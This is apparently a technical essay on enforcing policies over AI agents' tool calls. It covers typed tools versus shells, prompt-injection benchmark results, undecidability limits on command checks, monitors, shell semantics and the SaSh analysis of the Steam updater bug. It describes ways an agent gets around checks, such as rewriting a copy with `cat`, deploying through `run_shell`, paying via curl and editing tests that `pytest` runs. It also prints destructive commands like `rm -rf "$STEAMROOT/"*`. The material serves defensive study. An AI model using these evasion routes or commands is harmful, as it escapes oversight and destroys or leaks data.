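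To test the policies, the developers assumed that an attacker fully controlled the agent and could fool every language model that read untrusted text. They then looked for any permitted sequence of calls that would achieve the attacker's goal. On AgentDojo, a benchmark of short office, travel and banking tasks, the policies ruled out 93% to 95% of the attacks, depending on which model wrote the policies. Lists of allowed tools ruled out 83% to 87%. On the full set of Toolathlon, which has longer tasks and attacks that use the same tools as the task, the policies ruled out 65% of the attacks and the lists ruled out 32%.

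Agents with policies finished only one to five fewer of AgentDojo's 97 tasks than agents without them. Some failures occurred because the language model writing the policy had to guess about data it had no access to. One policy required the name "London Luxury Hotel", but the database listed the hotel as "London Luxury". Tasks also took longer, mostly because of the time spent writing each policy. The average Toolathlon task took 679 seconds, compared with 548 without a policy.

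More than 80% of the successful attacks on each benchmark depended on the meaning of a text. Most of them used content that the agent wrote, such as a file or the body of a message. In one Toolathlon attack, the agent changes a candidate's rejection to "strong hire" in a summary of interview feedback. The tool, the file and the order of calls are correct, and only the open argument is wrong.

### Small checks that read the database

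Checks on typed arguments can also help an agent finish its work. Reddy, Challaram and Basu tested this in *Reason Less, Verify More* (2026) on the airline tasks of τ²-bench, a benchmark in which agents handle customer service requests. The agent must follow the airline's rules, which are in a document, but the tools don't enforce them. If the agent asks to cancel a nonrefundable booking, the tool cancels it and reports success. Of the failures the team observed, 78% left the database in the wrong state without an error message.

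The team put four small checks, called gates, in front of the tools that change bookings. One gate blocks cancellations that break the rules on fare type, timing, insurance and flights already taken. Another checks baggage allowances, and a third blocks any change to the number of passengers. The last requires the agent to read a record before changing it. Each gate is an ordinary function of the tool's name, its arguments and the current database. A gate that rejects a call returns a reason, and the agent can then try something else.

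With GPT-4o mini, an older and fairly small model, the gates raised the success rate from 29.6% to 42.0% over 250 attempts each. A repeat with 750 attempts each gave almost the same gain. The share of tasks the agent completed in all five attempts rose from 8% to 26%. With GPT-5.2, the success rate rose from 61.2% to 71.6%, but the team didn't repeat that test.

The gain came mainly from tasks in which a gate blocked something. On those tasks, the smaller model's success rate rose from 13.8% to 33.1%. The change on the other tasks was small enough to be due to chance. The gates also made little difference on two other sets of tasks. In one, which covered retail, the tools already refused forbidden changes. In the other, the agents' mistakes usually caused visible errors.

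The team compared each blocked call with a correct solution to the task. All 161 calls that the cancellation gate blocked were mistakes, but only two of the 42 that the baggage gate blocked were. Baggage rules are no more open-ended than cancellation rules, so typed arguments make a precise check possible but don't guarantee that someone will write one.

Reddy and colleagues note that the reason given with each rejection may explain part of the gain, since the agent learns from it what to fix. They also tested the gates on the same tasks they had used to write them. If a gate crashes, their system lets the call through. This avoids blocking good calls, but it means the bound holds only if the gate never fails.

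### Paths, web addresses and record numbers

The cancellation gate needs the database because a reservation number doesn't show the fare or whether the passenger has already flown. In one task, the customer lies about the booking to get a cancellation. The agent handled this task correctly in all 16 attempts with the gates, and in at most one of 16 without them. A check of the call alone would have found a well-formed reservation number every time.

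All references have this problem to some degree. Suppose the release agent has a tool `read_file(path)`, and a rule allows only paths that begin with `public/`. The path `public/../secrets.txt` satisfies the rule but leads out of the folder. A stricter check can reject paths containing `..`, but `public/notes.txt` may be a link to the secret file, and nothing in the path would show it. Sistla and colleagues found that an early version of their own monitor missed hard links, which give the same file more than one name.

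A rule may allow `fetch(url)` only for addresses on `docs.example.com`, but that server can respond with a redirect, which is an instruction to load a page from somewhere else. If the tool follows the redirect automatically, it loads a page whose address was never checked.

A typed tool can recover the bound by looking up the reference and applying the rule to the result. The file tool can open the file and confirm that it is really in the public folder. The web tool can check each new address before following a redirect, and the airline tool can read the reservation. These checks require more than examining syntax, but they are still simple because the tool's definition specifies exactly what to look up.

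The result of a lookup can be out of date by the time the tool acts on it. If the tool checks a path and then opens it, another program can replace the file with a link in between. The tool avoids this by opening the file first and then checking the open file. For a database record, the check and the change should be in the same transaction. The version numbers in `deploy` avoid the problem because what each one refers to never changes.

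### The same rule for typed tools and for a shell

Sistla and colleagues compared several policy languages by writing the same rule in each. The rule covers the example from the previous section, in which an agent may upload a harmless report but not after copying a confidential inventory over it. Cedar can't distinguish the two uploads because both calls have the same arguments and Cedar doesn't check earlier calls.

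Dogwood can tell them apart if the agent has typed tools for copying, writing and uploading files. The rule forbids uploading a file if the agent copied the inventory to it within the past 24 hours and hasn't rewritten it since. If the agent has only a shell, the rule has to search for a past command instead. The main conditions of the two versions are:

```
CopyFile { src: "data/servers.csv", dst: context.input.path }

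Shell { command: "cp data/servers.csv scratch/report.txt" }
```

In the typed version, `context.input.path` stands for whichever file the agent is trying to upload, so the rule works for every destination. The shell version matches only one exact command, so the agent can get around it with `cat data/servers.csv > scratch/report.txt`, which makes the same copy. The policy can't compare the copied file with the uploaded file because it can't extract a file name from a past command.

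Part of this weakness is specific to Dogwood, which can match a past command only exactly or with a wildcard for the whole field. A language with better text patterns could find the file names in a plain `cp` command. But `python sync.py` can make the same copy, and its text contains neither name.

Typed tools don't make the rule complete either. If the agent copies the inventory to a temporary file and then copies that file over the report, the rule misses it. Dogwood needs another rule for two copies, and another for three. If $m$ different tools can copy a file, covering chains of up to $k$ copies takes

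$$m + m^2 + \dots + m^k$$

patterns. Three such tools and chains of up to four copies already require 120. A pattern for four copies also needs four temporal operators, and AWS allows only three per policy in its hosted service.

A broader rule could block the upload of any file written after the agent read the inventory. This catches chains of copies of any length, but it also blocks a report that the agent copied from a public template. Systems such as Tether avoid this tradeoff by attaching a label to each file and passing it on with every copy. With typed tools, a monitor can track these labels from the arguments alone, because the arguments for each copy include its source and destination.

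### What typed tools cost

A typed tool does only what its designer planned for, so some tasks will have no suitable tool. Toolathlon gives agents more than 600 tools for 32 applications, and a few of its tasks still call for arbitrary computation. *Sapien* removed the Python execution tool from every agent it tested, which affected those tasks. It kept the terminal but required each policy to restrict the terminal's commands, for example to the search program `grep`. The defense rates on Toolathlon therefore apply to agents without a general way to run code.

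Coding agents would lose much more. Sistla and colleagues couldn't compare their system with Dogwood and a companion sandbox, Strands Box, on realistic programming tasks because the sandbox had its own limited shell and didn't support arbitrary Linux programs or general Python code. The researchers also judged the policy language too weak to express useful rules about shell commands.

It may seem reasonable to provide typed tools for most of the work and a shell for the rest. But the bounds on the typed tools then no longer limit what the agent can do. Suppose the calls that a runtime admits to the typed tools have effects within the sets $B_1, \dots, B_n$, and the shell can do anything in the set $U$. The agent as a whole is limited only to

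$$B_1 \cup \dots \cup B_n \cup U.$$

For the release agent, a check on `deploy` might allow only versions 2.4.1 and 2.4.2. If the shell has access to the same deployment script and credentials, $U$ includes deploying any version, so the agent can still put version 3.0 into production with `run_shell("./deploy.sh 3.0")`. Counts and budgets fail in the same way, because a policy that adds up calls to `transfer` won't count a payment the agent makes with `curl`.

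The shell can also make a typed tool's bound false. A sound check has to hold in every state that can arise, and the shell makes more states possible. If the agent can overwrite the stored files for version 2.4.1, `deploy("2.4.1")` passes the check but puts different software into production. The argument that the check is sound relied partly on the company's promise never to reuse a version number, which a single shell command can break.

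A narrow filter on the shell, such as allowing only `grep`, helps if it reliably blocks commands that deploy software or change the stored builds. Otherwise the company has to run the shell under an account that lacks permission to do either, so that the operating system enforces the limit.

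## What a check on text can guarantee about effects

A company that allows `grep` on its build machine will soon want to allow more commands. How far it can safely widen the filter depends on what a program can work out about a command's effects from the command's text.

As before, let $B$ be the permitted effects and $E(w,s)$ the effects of a call with argument $w$ in state $s$. The harmless arguments are those whose effects always stay within $B$:

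$$H = \{\, w : E(w,s) \subseteq B \ \text{ for every } s \,\}.$$

A syntactic check is defined by the set $A$ of arguments it admits. It is sound when $A \subseteq H$ and exact when $A = H$, so an exact check blocks every harmful command and no harmless ones. Suppose $B$ contains every effect except the deletion of a file called `customers.csv`. Could anyone write an exact check for `run_shell`?

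### Why no check is exact

The answer is no, given three premises:

1. The argument can express any program. This holds for `command`, because bash is a full programming language and can also start Python.
2. The rule concerns what a program does, and some programs obey it while others break it.
3. The check always finishes and gives an answer.

The proof relies on the halting problem, which Alan Turing showed to be unsolvable in 1936. Suppose a program $D$ could always determine whether a given program eventually stops on a given input. Someone could then write a program $G$ that reads a program's text and uses $D$ to check whether that program would stop when run on its own text. $G$ loops forever if $D$ outputs yes and stops if $D$ outputs no. When $G$ runs on its own text, $D$'s output is wrong either way, so $D$ can't exist.

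Now take any program $M$ and write this command:

```
python3 -c "<simulator containing M>" && rm customers.csv
```

The simulator carries out $M$'s steps in memory and touches no files. If $M$ stops, the shell then runs `rm` and deletes the file. Otherwise, the shell never reaches `rm`, and the command is harmless. An exact check could therefore be used to determine whether $M$ stops for every $M$, which no program can do.

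Rice's theorem (1953) extends this to every rule that fits the second premise. Rice considered the results that programs return, but a program can delete a file without ever returning anything. Amer, Kinczel and Long (2026), in *No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard*, therefore prove a version for the sequence of actions a program performs. *Intent-Driven Computing* (2026) gives "This agent stays within its refund limit" as an example of an undecidable rule. A single comparison can check this rule for a tool with a `refundAmount` field, but the rule becomes undecidable when the agent can write the program that issues the refunds.

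Even short, readable programs can be hard to certify as safe. Pérez-Acle (2026), in *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program*, describes one that goes through the even numbers from 4 upward and performs a forbidden operation if it finds one that isn't the sum of two primes. The program is safe if and only if Goldbach's conjecture is true, which nobody had proved when he wrote. In his simulation, a test that ran the program for a million steps found nothing wrong.

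Dropping the third premise doesn't help. Pérez-Acle considers checks that may search forever for a certificate, meaning a finite piece of evidence that a program is safe. Suppose every safe program had a certificate and no unsafe program did. We could then solve the halting problem by running $M$ while searching for a certificate for the command above, since one of the two must eventually succeed. A harmful program, however, can be proved harmful by running it until it does the damage.

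The theorem also applies when the check is a language model, since a language model is a program. Randomness doesn't avoid it either. Amer and colleagues prove that for any undecidable rule, every randomized check is wrong at least half the time on some argument.

Lists of programs have the same problem. Franco and Gershenson (2026), in *Pandora's Toolbox Or Why Agent Safety Cannot Be Verified*, point out that infinitely many programs behave identically to any given one, so no finite list of banned programs covers them all. A list of approved programs fails if it includes an interpreter such as Python, because the agent can give the interpreter a dangerous program as data.

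### When the effect depends on the project's files

The earlier examples mostly assumed that the agent can't edit the test suite. Suppose it can, and the release manager approves the command `pytest`, which runs the Python tests in the project folder. If the agent adds a test that deletes `customers.csv`, the approved command will delete the file.

In the notation above, there is a state $s$ for which $E(\texttt{pytest}, s) \not\subseteq B$, so `pytest` is not in $H$. A sound syntactic check therefore has to reject it, even in states where the tests are harmless.

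The text of the command doesn't contain the necessary information, so this argument would hold even if `pytest` were the only command the agent could issue and the check had unlimited computing power. It doesn't use Rice's theorem. *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider, 2006) distinguishes mechanisms that can't observe the events a policy depends on from those that can observe them but lack the power to compute the answer. A different mechanism might work in the second case, but in the first, any mechanism with the same observations will also fail.

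The check could also read the test files, but those files are programs, so Rice's theorem applies to them. A more practical solution is for a person to review the files once. Before each run, the check then computes a cryptographic fingerprint of the files and refuses the command if it differs from the reviewed version's fingerprint. The fingerprint must cover everything the tests load, including installed libraries, and the files must not change between the comparison and the run.

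Typed tools can have a similar gap between reading something and acting on it. *Mind the Gap* (2025) describes a benchmark of AgentDojo tasks that need at least two tool calls. The researchers hand-labeled the tasks in which one call reads something, such as a calendar, and a later call assumes it hasn't changed. According to *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026), the benchmark has 66 tasks, and a combination of rewritten prompts, state monitoring and merged tools cut the rate of such flaws in agents' runs from 12% to 8%.

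### How much a sound check can admit

A sound check, one that admits no harmful command, always exists. A company can refuse every command, or admit only commands from a small language whose effects somebody has proved harmless. Both checks also refuse some harmless commands.

When no exact check exists, any sound check refuses infinitely many harmless commands. If it refused only finitely many, adding them to the commands it admits would make it exact.

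Pérez-Acle shows how to construct one of these commands. The command runs the check on the command's own text, deletes the file if the check admits the command, and otherwise does nothing. A sound check can't admit this command, so the command does nothing and is harmless. It is also only a little longer than the check. Pérez-Acle built such commands for four sound checks of 64 to 409 characters, and each command was fewer than 950 characters longer than its check.

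A release agent loses nothing if it can't run programs like that. What matters is whether the check admits the commands the agent needs. If $O$ is the set of those commands, the company needs a set $A$ with

$$O \subseteq A \subseteq H,$$

and it needs an algorithm that always decides whether a command is in $A$. For the release agent, $O$ might contain commands for listing files and searching logs. The company can then ignore the rest of $H$, including every harmless program that nobody would want to run.

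A crude check may still reject many safe programs. Pérez-Acle examined every possible program in a toy model with a few states, using a check that admits a program only if the forbidden operation appears nowhere in it. The check admitted 71.9% of the safe programs with three states, but only 47.3% of those with five. Many of the larger programs contained the forbidden operation but never reached it.

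More encouragingly, Amer and colleagues prove that for any rule and any fixed pattern of use, a sound check can refuse harmless commands as rarely as one likes, given a long enough list of correctly judged commands. Suppose 99% of an agent's commands come from a list of 5,000, and someone judges each entry correctly. A check that admits the harmless entries and refuses everything else is sound, and it refuses a harmless command at most 1% of the time. But someone has to judge every entry, and Amer and colleagues also prove that for an undecidable rule, no single algorithm can do this for every list. Commands like `pytest` still have to stay off the list unless the company controls the files they run.

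### Questions about text that always have an answer

Most practical checks rely on questions about text that a program can always answer. The simplest is whether a command matches a regular pattern, such as `git (status|log|diff)`, which matches three commands. A finite automaton can test this in one pass, taking one step per character.

A program can also decide whether every string that matches one regular pattern matches another, which is useful when someone edits a list of allowed commands. Suppose an edit adds `push`, so the new pattern is `git (status|log|diff|push)`. The program builds an automaton for strings that match the new pattern but not the old one, and looks for a string it accepts. Here it finds `git push`, so the edit has made the policy more permissive.

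Context-free grammars can describe unlimited nesting, such as correctly matched brackets, which regular patterns can't. They can also describe the basic structure of formats such as JSON. An algorithm can always decide whether a string belongs to a context-free language, but no algorithm can decide for every pair of context-free languages whether one contains the other.

| Question | Regular patterns | Context-free grammars |
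|---|---|---|
| Does this string belong to the set? | Decidable | Decidable |
| Does one set contain the other? | Decidable | Undecidable |

The undecidable entry also comes from the halting problem. We can write any halting run of a program $M$ as a string that lists its configurations in order. For each $M$, there is a context-free grammar that generates every string except correct records of such runs, because a single error makes a record incorrect and a grammar can describe each kind of error. This grammar generates all strings exactly when $M$ never halts. Deciding whether the grammar's language contains the language of all strings would therefore solve the halting problem.

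A policy author can often avoid undecidability by writing the policy as a regular pattern. If the agent's arguments follow a context-free grammar, an algorithm can then decide whether every possible argument matches the policy.

Matching a command against a pattern checks only its text. Someone has to prove separately that every command matching the pattern is harmless, and this can be harder than it looks. A git repository's settings can name an external program for `git diff` to run, so an agent that can edit the settings can make this apparently read-only command run any program. The shell also expands some parts of a command before running it, so the text a pattern matches may differ from what the shell executes.

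### Static checks, monitors and rewriters

A static check accepts or rejects a program before it runs. Hamlen and colleagues compared static checks with monitors, which watch a program as it runs, and rewriters, which change it beforehand. They asked which policies each mechanism can enforce without interfering with programs that already comply.

| Mechanism | Policies it can enforce | Example |
|---|---|---|
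| Static check | Those that an algorithm can decide | The program stops within 100 steps |
| Monitor | Those whose violations an algorithm can always detect in finite time, provided the monitor can act soon enough | The program never writes to the disk's boot sector |
| Rewriter | No standard class matches | The program behaves as if a secret file didn't exist |

A static check can enforce the 100-step limit by simulating the program on every possible input of 100 symbols, since the program can't read more than that in 100 steps. It can't exactly enforce the rule against writing to the boot sector, because deciding whether a program will ever write there is as hard as the halting problem.

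A monitor waits until the program is about to write to the boot sector and then stops it, so it doesn't need to predict whether the program will do so. Schneider showed that such a monitor can enforce only safety properties, and later work added that the monitor must be able to compute whether a finite run has violated the property.

Hamlen and colleagues found that even this isn't enough, because a monitor may detect a violation too late. In their example, a service lends a resource to a program and can't take it back. When the program announces that it has finished, the service lends the resource to another program. The rule is that no program may use the resource after announcing this. A monitor can detect the forbidden use, but by then two programs may have the resource. To prevent this, the monitor would have to know at the time of the announcement whether the program will ever use the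 resource again.

Tool calls often have effects that nobody can reverse. Ray considers the rule that a confirmation must eventually follow every payment. A mechanism that can hold actions back could delay each payment until the agent issues the confirmation. A gate that must decide on each payment immediately can't enforce the rule, because the right decision depends on whether a confirmation will follow. Ray proves that such a gate can enforce a rule exactly when three conditions hold: the rule is a safety property, at least one sequence of actions satisfies it, and the gate can compute whether the actions so far are still acceptable.

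A rewriter must produce a program that obeys the policy and preserve the behavior of any program that already obeys it. For the secret-file policy, it can change every request for a directory listing so that the result omits the file. A program that would have ignored the file behaves as before, and any other program can no longer react to it. No algorithm can tell these two kinds of program apart in general, but the rewriter doesn't need to. Rewriters still cannot enforce some rules, such as requiring a program to stop on at least one input.

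A gate in front of `run_shell` handles each call as a single event, but that call may contain an entire program. The gate can therefore monitor the sequence of calls and enforce rules about their order. Within a command, it has only the power of a static check, because it must decide before the command runs. Stopping a deletion just before it happens requires monitoring the command during execution.

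Monitoring an agent's actions doesn't help when the harm lies in the content of a file or message. Amer and colleagues prove that a monitor can exactly enforce a ban on specified actions if it sees every action and can stop it. But if the rule forbids sending customers a script that would delete their files, the monitor has to determine what a script would do before the agent sends it.

### Rules that no single run can settle

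Secrecy is one of the rules that can't be checked from a single run, so monitors can't enforce it exactly. *Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) gives a general account of such rules. It represents a system as the set $T$ of all its possible runs. An ordinary rule is a set $P$ of acceptable runs, and the system obeys it if $T \subseteq P$. A hyperproperty is a set $\mathbf{Q}$ of acceptable systems, and the system obeys it if $T \in \mathbf{Q}$.

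One example is noninterference, which requires that secret inputs have no influence on what the public sees. In one version, for deterministic systems, every run $t$ must have a counterpart $t'$ with no secret inputs and the same public events:

$$\forall t \in T \;\; \exists t' \in T : \ \text{secret}(t') = \varnothing \ \text{ and } \ \text{public}(t') = \text{public}(t).$$

Like secrecy, a requirement that the average response time over all runs be under one second is a hyperproperty, because a slow run may be acceptable if most others are fast.

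Blocking some of a system's runs can break a hyperproperty, though it can never break a safety property. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that arbitrarily chooses to output 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit. Its possible outputs are 0 and 1 whatever the secret is, so it obeys the rule that possible outputs must not depend on the secret. If we keep only the runs that output the secret bit, the system breaks that rule.

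A gate can cause a leak by blocking messages. Suppose an agent sends the same monthly notice to every customer, and a gate blocks notices to customers on a confidential list of fraud suspects. A customer who doesn't receive the notice could infer that they are on the list, even though every message the gate allowed was harmless.

Analyzing a program instead of watching it run can't always show whether it leaks a secret. Pérez-Acle considers programs that receive one of two secrets and must publish the same sequence of values in both cases, ignoring timing. Outputs that match so far may still differ later, and if one is shorter, the program may have stopped or may just be slow. As a result, no procedure can confirm every program that keeps the secret or every program that leaks it.

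Longer tests don't remove this problem. Pérez-Acle compared the two outputs of each random program after a fixed number of steps. Tests longer than 64 steps all wrongly rejected between 0.03% and 0.37% of the programs that kept the secret, depending on the program's length. In the longest tests, all the errors came from programs that published the same endless sequence at different speeds.

### Finite machines, time limits and simple commands

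The halting problem assumes unlimited memory, which real computers don't have. A machine with $m$ bits of memory has at most $2^m$ configurations. If a program confined to that memory hasn't deleted the file after $2^m$ steps, it has repeated a configuration and will repeat the same steps forever. So an exact check exists, but it isn't practical, because $2^m$ is already about $10^{90}$ with just 300 bits of memory.

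Pérez-Acle proves that any always-correct check, however well designed, takes time that grows in proportion to $2^m$ in the worst case, and that it needs almost as much memory as the programs it checks. Franco and Gershenson show that predicting the safety of an agent with bounded memory and running time is PSPACE-complete, so researchers expect no efficient general method for it.

Most agent runtimes stop commands after a time limit. If the limit is $T$ steps, a check can simulate the command for $T$ steps and observe what it does. But no check that is always correct can be much faster than this on every program. For any check, there is a program that runs the check on its own text and then does the opposite of what the check predicts. If the check finishes early enough for the program to do this before the limit, the prediction is wrong.

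Pérez-Acle tested this with eight checks and limits from 8 to 1,024 steps, writing a program to try to defeat each check. The check that simulated the whole period was always right, and the other seven were always wrong, including one that simulated half the period and one that searched the text for the forbidden operation. A company that needs correct answers for all programs might as well run the command in an isolated copy of the machine, provided the copy reproduces the relevant state.

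A time limit also restricts only the command itself. In under a second, a command can schedule a deletion for midnight or edit a test that `pytest` will run tomorrow.

The best objection is that the commands agents normally write are nothing like these self-referential programs. Pérez-Acle's simulations support this. Among 2.2 million random programs, 1.6% performed the forbidden operation. An eight-step test missed up to 30.2% of those, depending on program length, but a 128-step test missed none. Random toy programs aren't shell commands, but the results suggest that hard cases are rare when nobody is looking for them.

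An attacker will look for them, and an agent that reads web pages or email may run commands an attacker has chosen. Amer and colleagues put a lower bound on the cost. If an attacker is behind a fraction $\alpha$ of uses, succeeds with probability $\sigma$ and causes a loss of at least $\lambda$ each time, the expected loss per use is at least

$$\alpha\,\sigma\,\lambda,$$

however accurate the check is on average. If one use in 10,000 is an attack, half of attacks succeed, and each success costs a million dollars, the expected loss is at least 50 dollars per use.

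An attacker may not need a complicated program either. Changing a file that `pytest` runs is enough.

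## Shell commands as arguments

An ordinary command can be hard to check even if nobody is attacking the machine. Suppose the release agent wants to archive its logs and calls `run_shell` with this argument:

```
tar -czf $DEST *.log
```

The program `tar` packs files into one archive. The agent expects the variable `DEST` to hold the archive's name. The pattern `*.log` matches every file in the current folder whose name ends in ".log". The company wants to allow the command to create the archive but prevent it from changing any other file.

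Before a shell command takes effect, the shell parses its text, expands variables and file patterns, and looks up the program. The program then reads its options and may start other programs.

*Executable Formal Semantics for the POSIX Shell* (Greenberg and Blatt, 2020) gives formal rules for the shell's part of this work. The rules follow POSIX, a standard that bash and similar shells implement with small differences. They also run as a working shell called Smoosh.

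### From text to effect

Parsing depends mostly on the text. Here the shell finds one command of four words, with no operator such as `|` or `&&` joining it to another. But `tar` may be an alias for something else. A shell also runs each line of a script before it reads the next, so an early line can change how it parses a later one.

Expansion depends far more on the environment. Greenberg and Blatt describe four stages. First, the shell replaces `~` with a home folder, `$DEST` with the variable's value, `$(...)` with the output of the command inside it, and `$((...))` with the result of a calculation. Second, it splits the results into words, normally at spaces, tabs and line breaks. Third, it replaces file patterns with the names of matching files. Fourth, it removes quotation marks.

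Suppose `DEST` holds `/backup/monday.tgz` and the folder contains `app.log` and `build.log`. The shell then runs what the agent intended:

```
tar -czf /backup/monday.tgz app.log build.log
```

If `DEST` holds `/backup/old logs/monday.tgz`, the second stage splits the value at the space, and `tar` writes an archive called `/backup/old`. If nobody has set `DEST`, the word disappears:

```
tar -czf app.log build.log
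```

Now `tar` treats `app.log` as the archive's name and overwrites it with an archive of the other log. Double-quoting `$DEST` would prevent both accidents, but a quoted variable can still hold the wrong filename.

A checker can't always avoid these problems by expanding the command first and inspecting the result, because expansion can have side effects. The shell has to run the command inside `$(...)` to get its output, and `$((y += x))` changes the value of `y`.

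The third step is to find the program. `tar` could be a function that an earlier call defined, a command built into the shell, or an executable file. For an executable, the shell searches the folders listed in the variable `PATH` and uses the first match. An agent that can write to a folder early in that list can change which program `tar` runs. The shell then starts a new process and has the operating system load the program into it. Greenberg and Blatt's rules don't cover what happens after that. Smoosh can simulate an operating system well enough to step through a script, but it can't run executables in that mode.

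The program receives a list of strings, and nothing in the list marks which ones are options. `tar` reads `-czf` as instructions to create an archive, compress it, and use the next string as the archive's name. If the pattern `*.log` matched a file whose name began with a hyphen, `tar` could read that name as an option. GNU `tar`, which most Linux systems use, also takes extra options from an environment variable.

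Finally, the program may start other programs. When given `-z`, GNU `tar` starts a separate compression program, which it also finds through `PATH`. Anything the compression program does is an effect of the call, even though its name doesn't appear in the command.

| Step | What the text fixes | What the environment supplies |
|---|---|---|
| Parsing | Words and operators | Aliases, and the shell that does the parsing |
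| Expansion | Which parts to replace, and which are in quotation marks | Values of variables, names of files, output of inner commands |
| Lookup | The program's name | Functions, the search path, and the files in it |
| Options | The strings in the command | The program's own conventions and settings |
| Other processes | At most a request for them | The programs that run and the files they load |

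The choice of shell matters because POSIX leaves many details open. Greenberg and Blatt counted 70 relevant uses of "unspecified" and 17 of "undefined" in the standard. One of their examples is this line:

```
f() { break; echo hi; }; while true; do f; break; done
```

Most shells print "hi". In zsh and an old version of bash that came with Apple's computers, the `break` inside the function ends the loop outside it, so they print nothing. If `echo hi` were replaced with a command that deletes a file, some shells would delete the file and others would not. The official POSIX test suite has 418 tests that apply in every locale. Smoosh passed them all, but the five other shells that could run the suite failed between 4 (bash) and 35 (mksh). A checker with its own parser can therefore misjudge what the host's shell will do.

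Greenberg, Kallas and Vasilakis (2021), in *Unix Shell Programming*, argue that any analysis of a script before it runs is either unsound, because it assumes that files and variables will be the same at run time, or ineffective, because it assumes the worst about everything that might change. For the archive command, the first assumption misses the overwritten log, and the second leads to a refusal every time, because `DEST` could name any file on the machine. Greenberg and colleagues suggest analyzing each command just before it runs, when its variables already have values. They want this mainly to make scripts faster, but it would also help a safety check. The check would no longer be syntactic, because it would read the state.

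### The Steam updater

In 2015, an update script for Steam, Valve's video game store, deleted the files of several Linux users. The script was supposed to clear out the old installation before installing a new one. Lazarek, Lamprou and colleagues, in *Ahead-of-time Analysis of Shell Program Effects*, trace the bug to two lines:

```
STEAMROOT="$(cd "${0%/*}" && echo $PWD)"
# ... 342 more lines ...
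rm -rf "$STEAMROOT/"*
```

The first line finds the folder that contains the script. `$0` is the path used to start the script, such as `/opt/steam/update.sh`. The expression `${0%/*}` removes the last slash and everything after it, which leaves `/opt/steam`. The script changes to that folder with `cd`. If this succeeds, `echo` prints the folder's full path, which the shell stores in `STEAMROOT`. The last line then deletes everything in `/opt/steam`.

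Suppose someone starts the script from its own folder as `update.sh`. The name has no slash to remove, so the script tries to change to a folder called `update.sh`. `cd` fails because `update.sh` is a file. Because of the `&&`, `echo` doesn't run, and `STEAMROOT` is empty. The last line becomes `rm -rf /*`, which deletes everything on the machine that the user has permission to delete.

The quotation marks are in the right places, and every command does what its manual describes. The text of the deletion is the same in both cases, and only the value of `STEAMROOT` differs. That value is set hundreds of lines earlier and depends on how someone started the script. A sound syntactic check that looked only at the last line would have to refuse the deletion, even though it usually removes just one folder.

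Checking the surrounding text for familiar patterns doesn't solve the problem. Lazarek, Jung and colleagues (2025), in *From Ahead-of- to Just-in-Time and Back Again*, compare two possible repairs. The first puts a condition around the deletion:

```
if [ "$(realpath "$STEAMROOT/")" != "/" ]; then
```

With this condition, the script deletes files only if the folder isn't the root of the file system. The second repair uses `=` instead of `!=`, so the script deletes files only if the folder is the root. ShellCheck, the standard tool for finding suspicious patterns in shell scripts, didn't detect that the first repair was safe or that the second was certain to be disastrous.

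### How SaSh finds such bugs

Lazarek, Lamprou and colleagues built SaSh, a system that analyzes a script's behavior without running it. It uses symbolic execution, which steps through a program with symbols in place of unknown values and records what must be true of those values on each path.

In the Steam script, the argument of `cd` depends on how the user started the program, so SaSh treats it as an unknown string. Because of the `&&`, the value of `STEAMROOT` depends on whether `cd` succeeds, so SaSh follows two execution paths. `STEAMROOT` equals the current folder if `cd` succeeds and is empty if it fails. When SaSh reaches the deletion, it adds the requirement that no deleted file path be critical, and a solver tests whether the requirement can hold. It can't hold when `cd` fails, so SaSh reports that the script may delete `/*` because `STEAMROOT` is empty.

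SaSh can't look inside `rm`, which is a separate program, so the team wrote specifications for common commands by hand. Each has three parts. For `rm -r p`, they are:

- Before the command, `p` should be a folder, or a file that some command has already read.
- If the command succeeds, `p` no longer exists.
- If the command fails, nothing has changed.

The condition about reading helps SaSh detect lost data. If a script moves one file to `x.txt` and then moves another file to the same name, the second move overwrites the first file before anything has read it.

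Writing specifications by hand is slow, so the 2025 paper proposes having a language model draft them from a command's manual. A test program would then run the command with many combinations of options and files and record what the command did.

Expansion needs a separate simplification, because an unknown variable has infinitely many possible values. SaSh keeps only three facts about such a value after expansion: any text that is certain to be at the start, any that is certain to be at the end, and the range of words it might split into. For the command `rm $1/usr`, where `$1` is the script's first input, SaSh records

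$$x \cdot \texttt{/usr}, \qquad \text{number of words} \in [1, \infty).$$

This is enough for SaSh to reveal a danger without listing the values of `$1` that would cause it. If `$1` ends with a space, `/usr` becomes a separate word, and the command targets the system's main folder of programs.

Long scripts have too many paths to explore in full. The Steam script has 83 explicit branching points between its two important lines. SaSh therefore begins with a quick search that follows only the side of each branch with more potentially destructive commands. It found the bug in the full 450-line script in 4.8 seconds. With this search and its other shortcuts, SaSh found a bug in a Debian installation script within 30 seconds, but without them it didn't find the bug in an hour.

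The team tested SaSh on 61 real scripts with 116 known bugs, including the Steam script. SaSh found 115 of the bugs within a minute per script, and 97 of them within a second. ShellCheck found 42, even though the team gave it credit for any warning related to the bug. On the repaired scripts, SaSh gave no warnings about the fixed bugs, but ShellCheck still warned about seven of the 42 it had found. When the team rewrote the scripts containing those 42 bugs without changing what they did, SaSh still found every bug and ShellCheck found none.

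These 116 bugs aren't a random sample. The team identified the eight kinds of fault SaSh looks for by studying the same scripts, and 18 of the bugs come from one backup script that uses the wrong comment symbol. But SaSh also found 70 new bugs in 44 open-source projects, including PyTorch and Kubernetes, and maintainers had accepted 27 of the fixes by the time the team wrote the paper.

### Why a clean report is not an effect bound

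SaSh assumes that a script runs under good conditions. Almost any shell script can do damage in some environment, so a tool that reported every possibility would warn about nearly every line. SaSh reports damage that happens even if the rest of the script goes well. Its warnings are therefore useful to a programmer, but a script without warnings may still be harmful.

The solver's question shows the difference. Let $P(x)$ be what SaSh knows about an unknown value $x$ on some path that a run could take, and let $A(x)$ be the requirement that the command delete nothing critical. SaSh warns if no possible value meets the requirement:

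$$\neg \exists x\,\big(P(x) \land A(x)\big).$$

A sound check would have to refuse the script if even one possible value broke the requirement:

$$\exists x\,\big(P(x) \land \neg A(x)\big).$$

A sound check refuses a script that deletes whatever folder its user names, because the user could name `/home`. SaSh doesn't warn about such a script, because the user could also name a folder of temporary files. For the same reason, SaSh missed one of the 116 bugs, in a Debian script that printed a list of packages and then deleted the folder the user had named. The deletion was a mistake only because the user had asked only for the list, which SaSh had no way to detect. The team could have made SaSh treat every named folder as critical, but it would then have raised many false alarms.

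Other assumptions also leave gaps:

- SaSh assumes that a command either succeeds completely or fails completely. In reality, `rm a b c` may delete two files and fail on the third.
- Outside explicit conditions, SaSh assumes that every command succeeds.
- If SaSh has no specification for a command, it assumes that the command has no effects.
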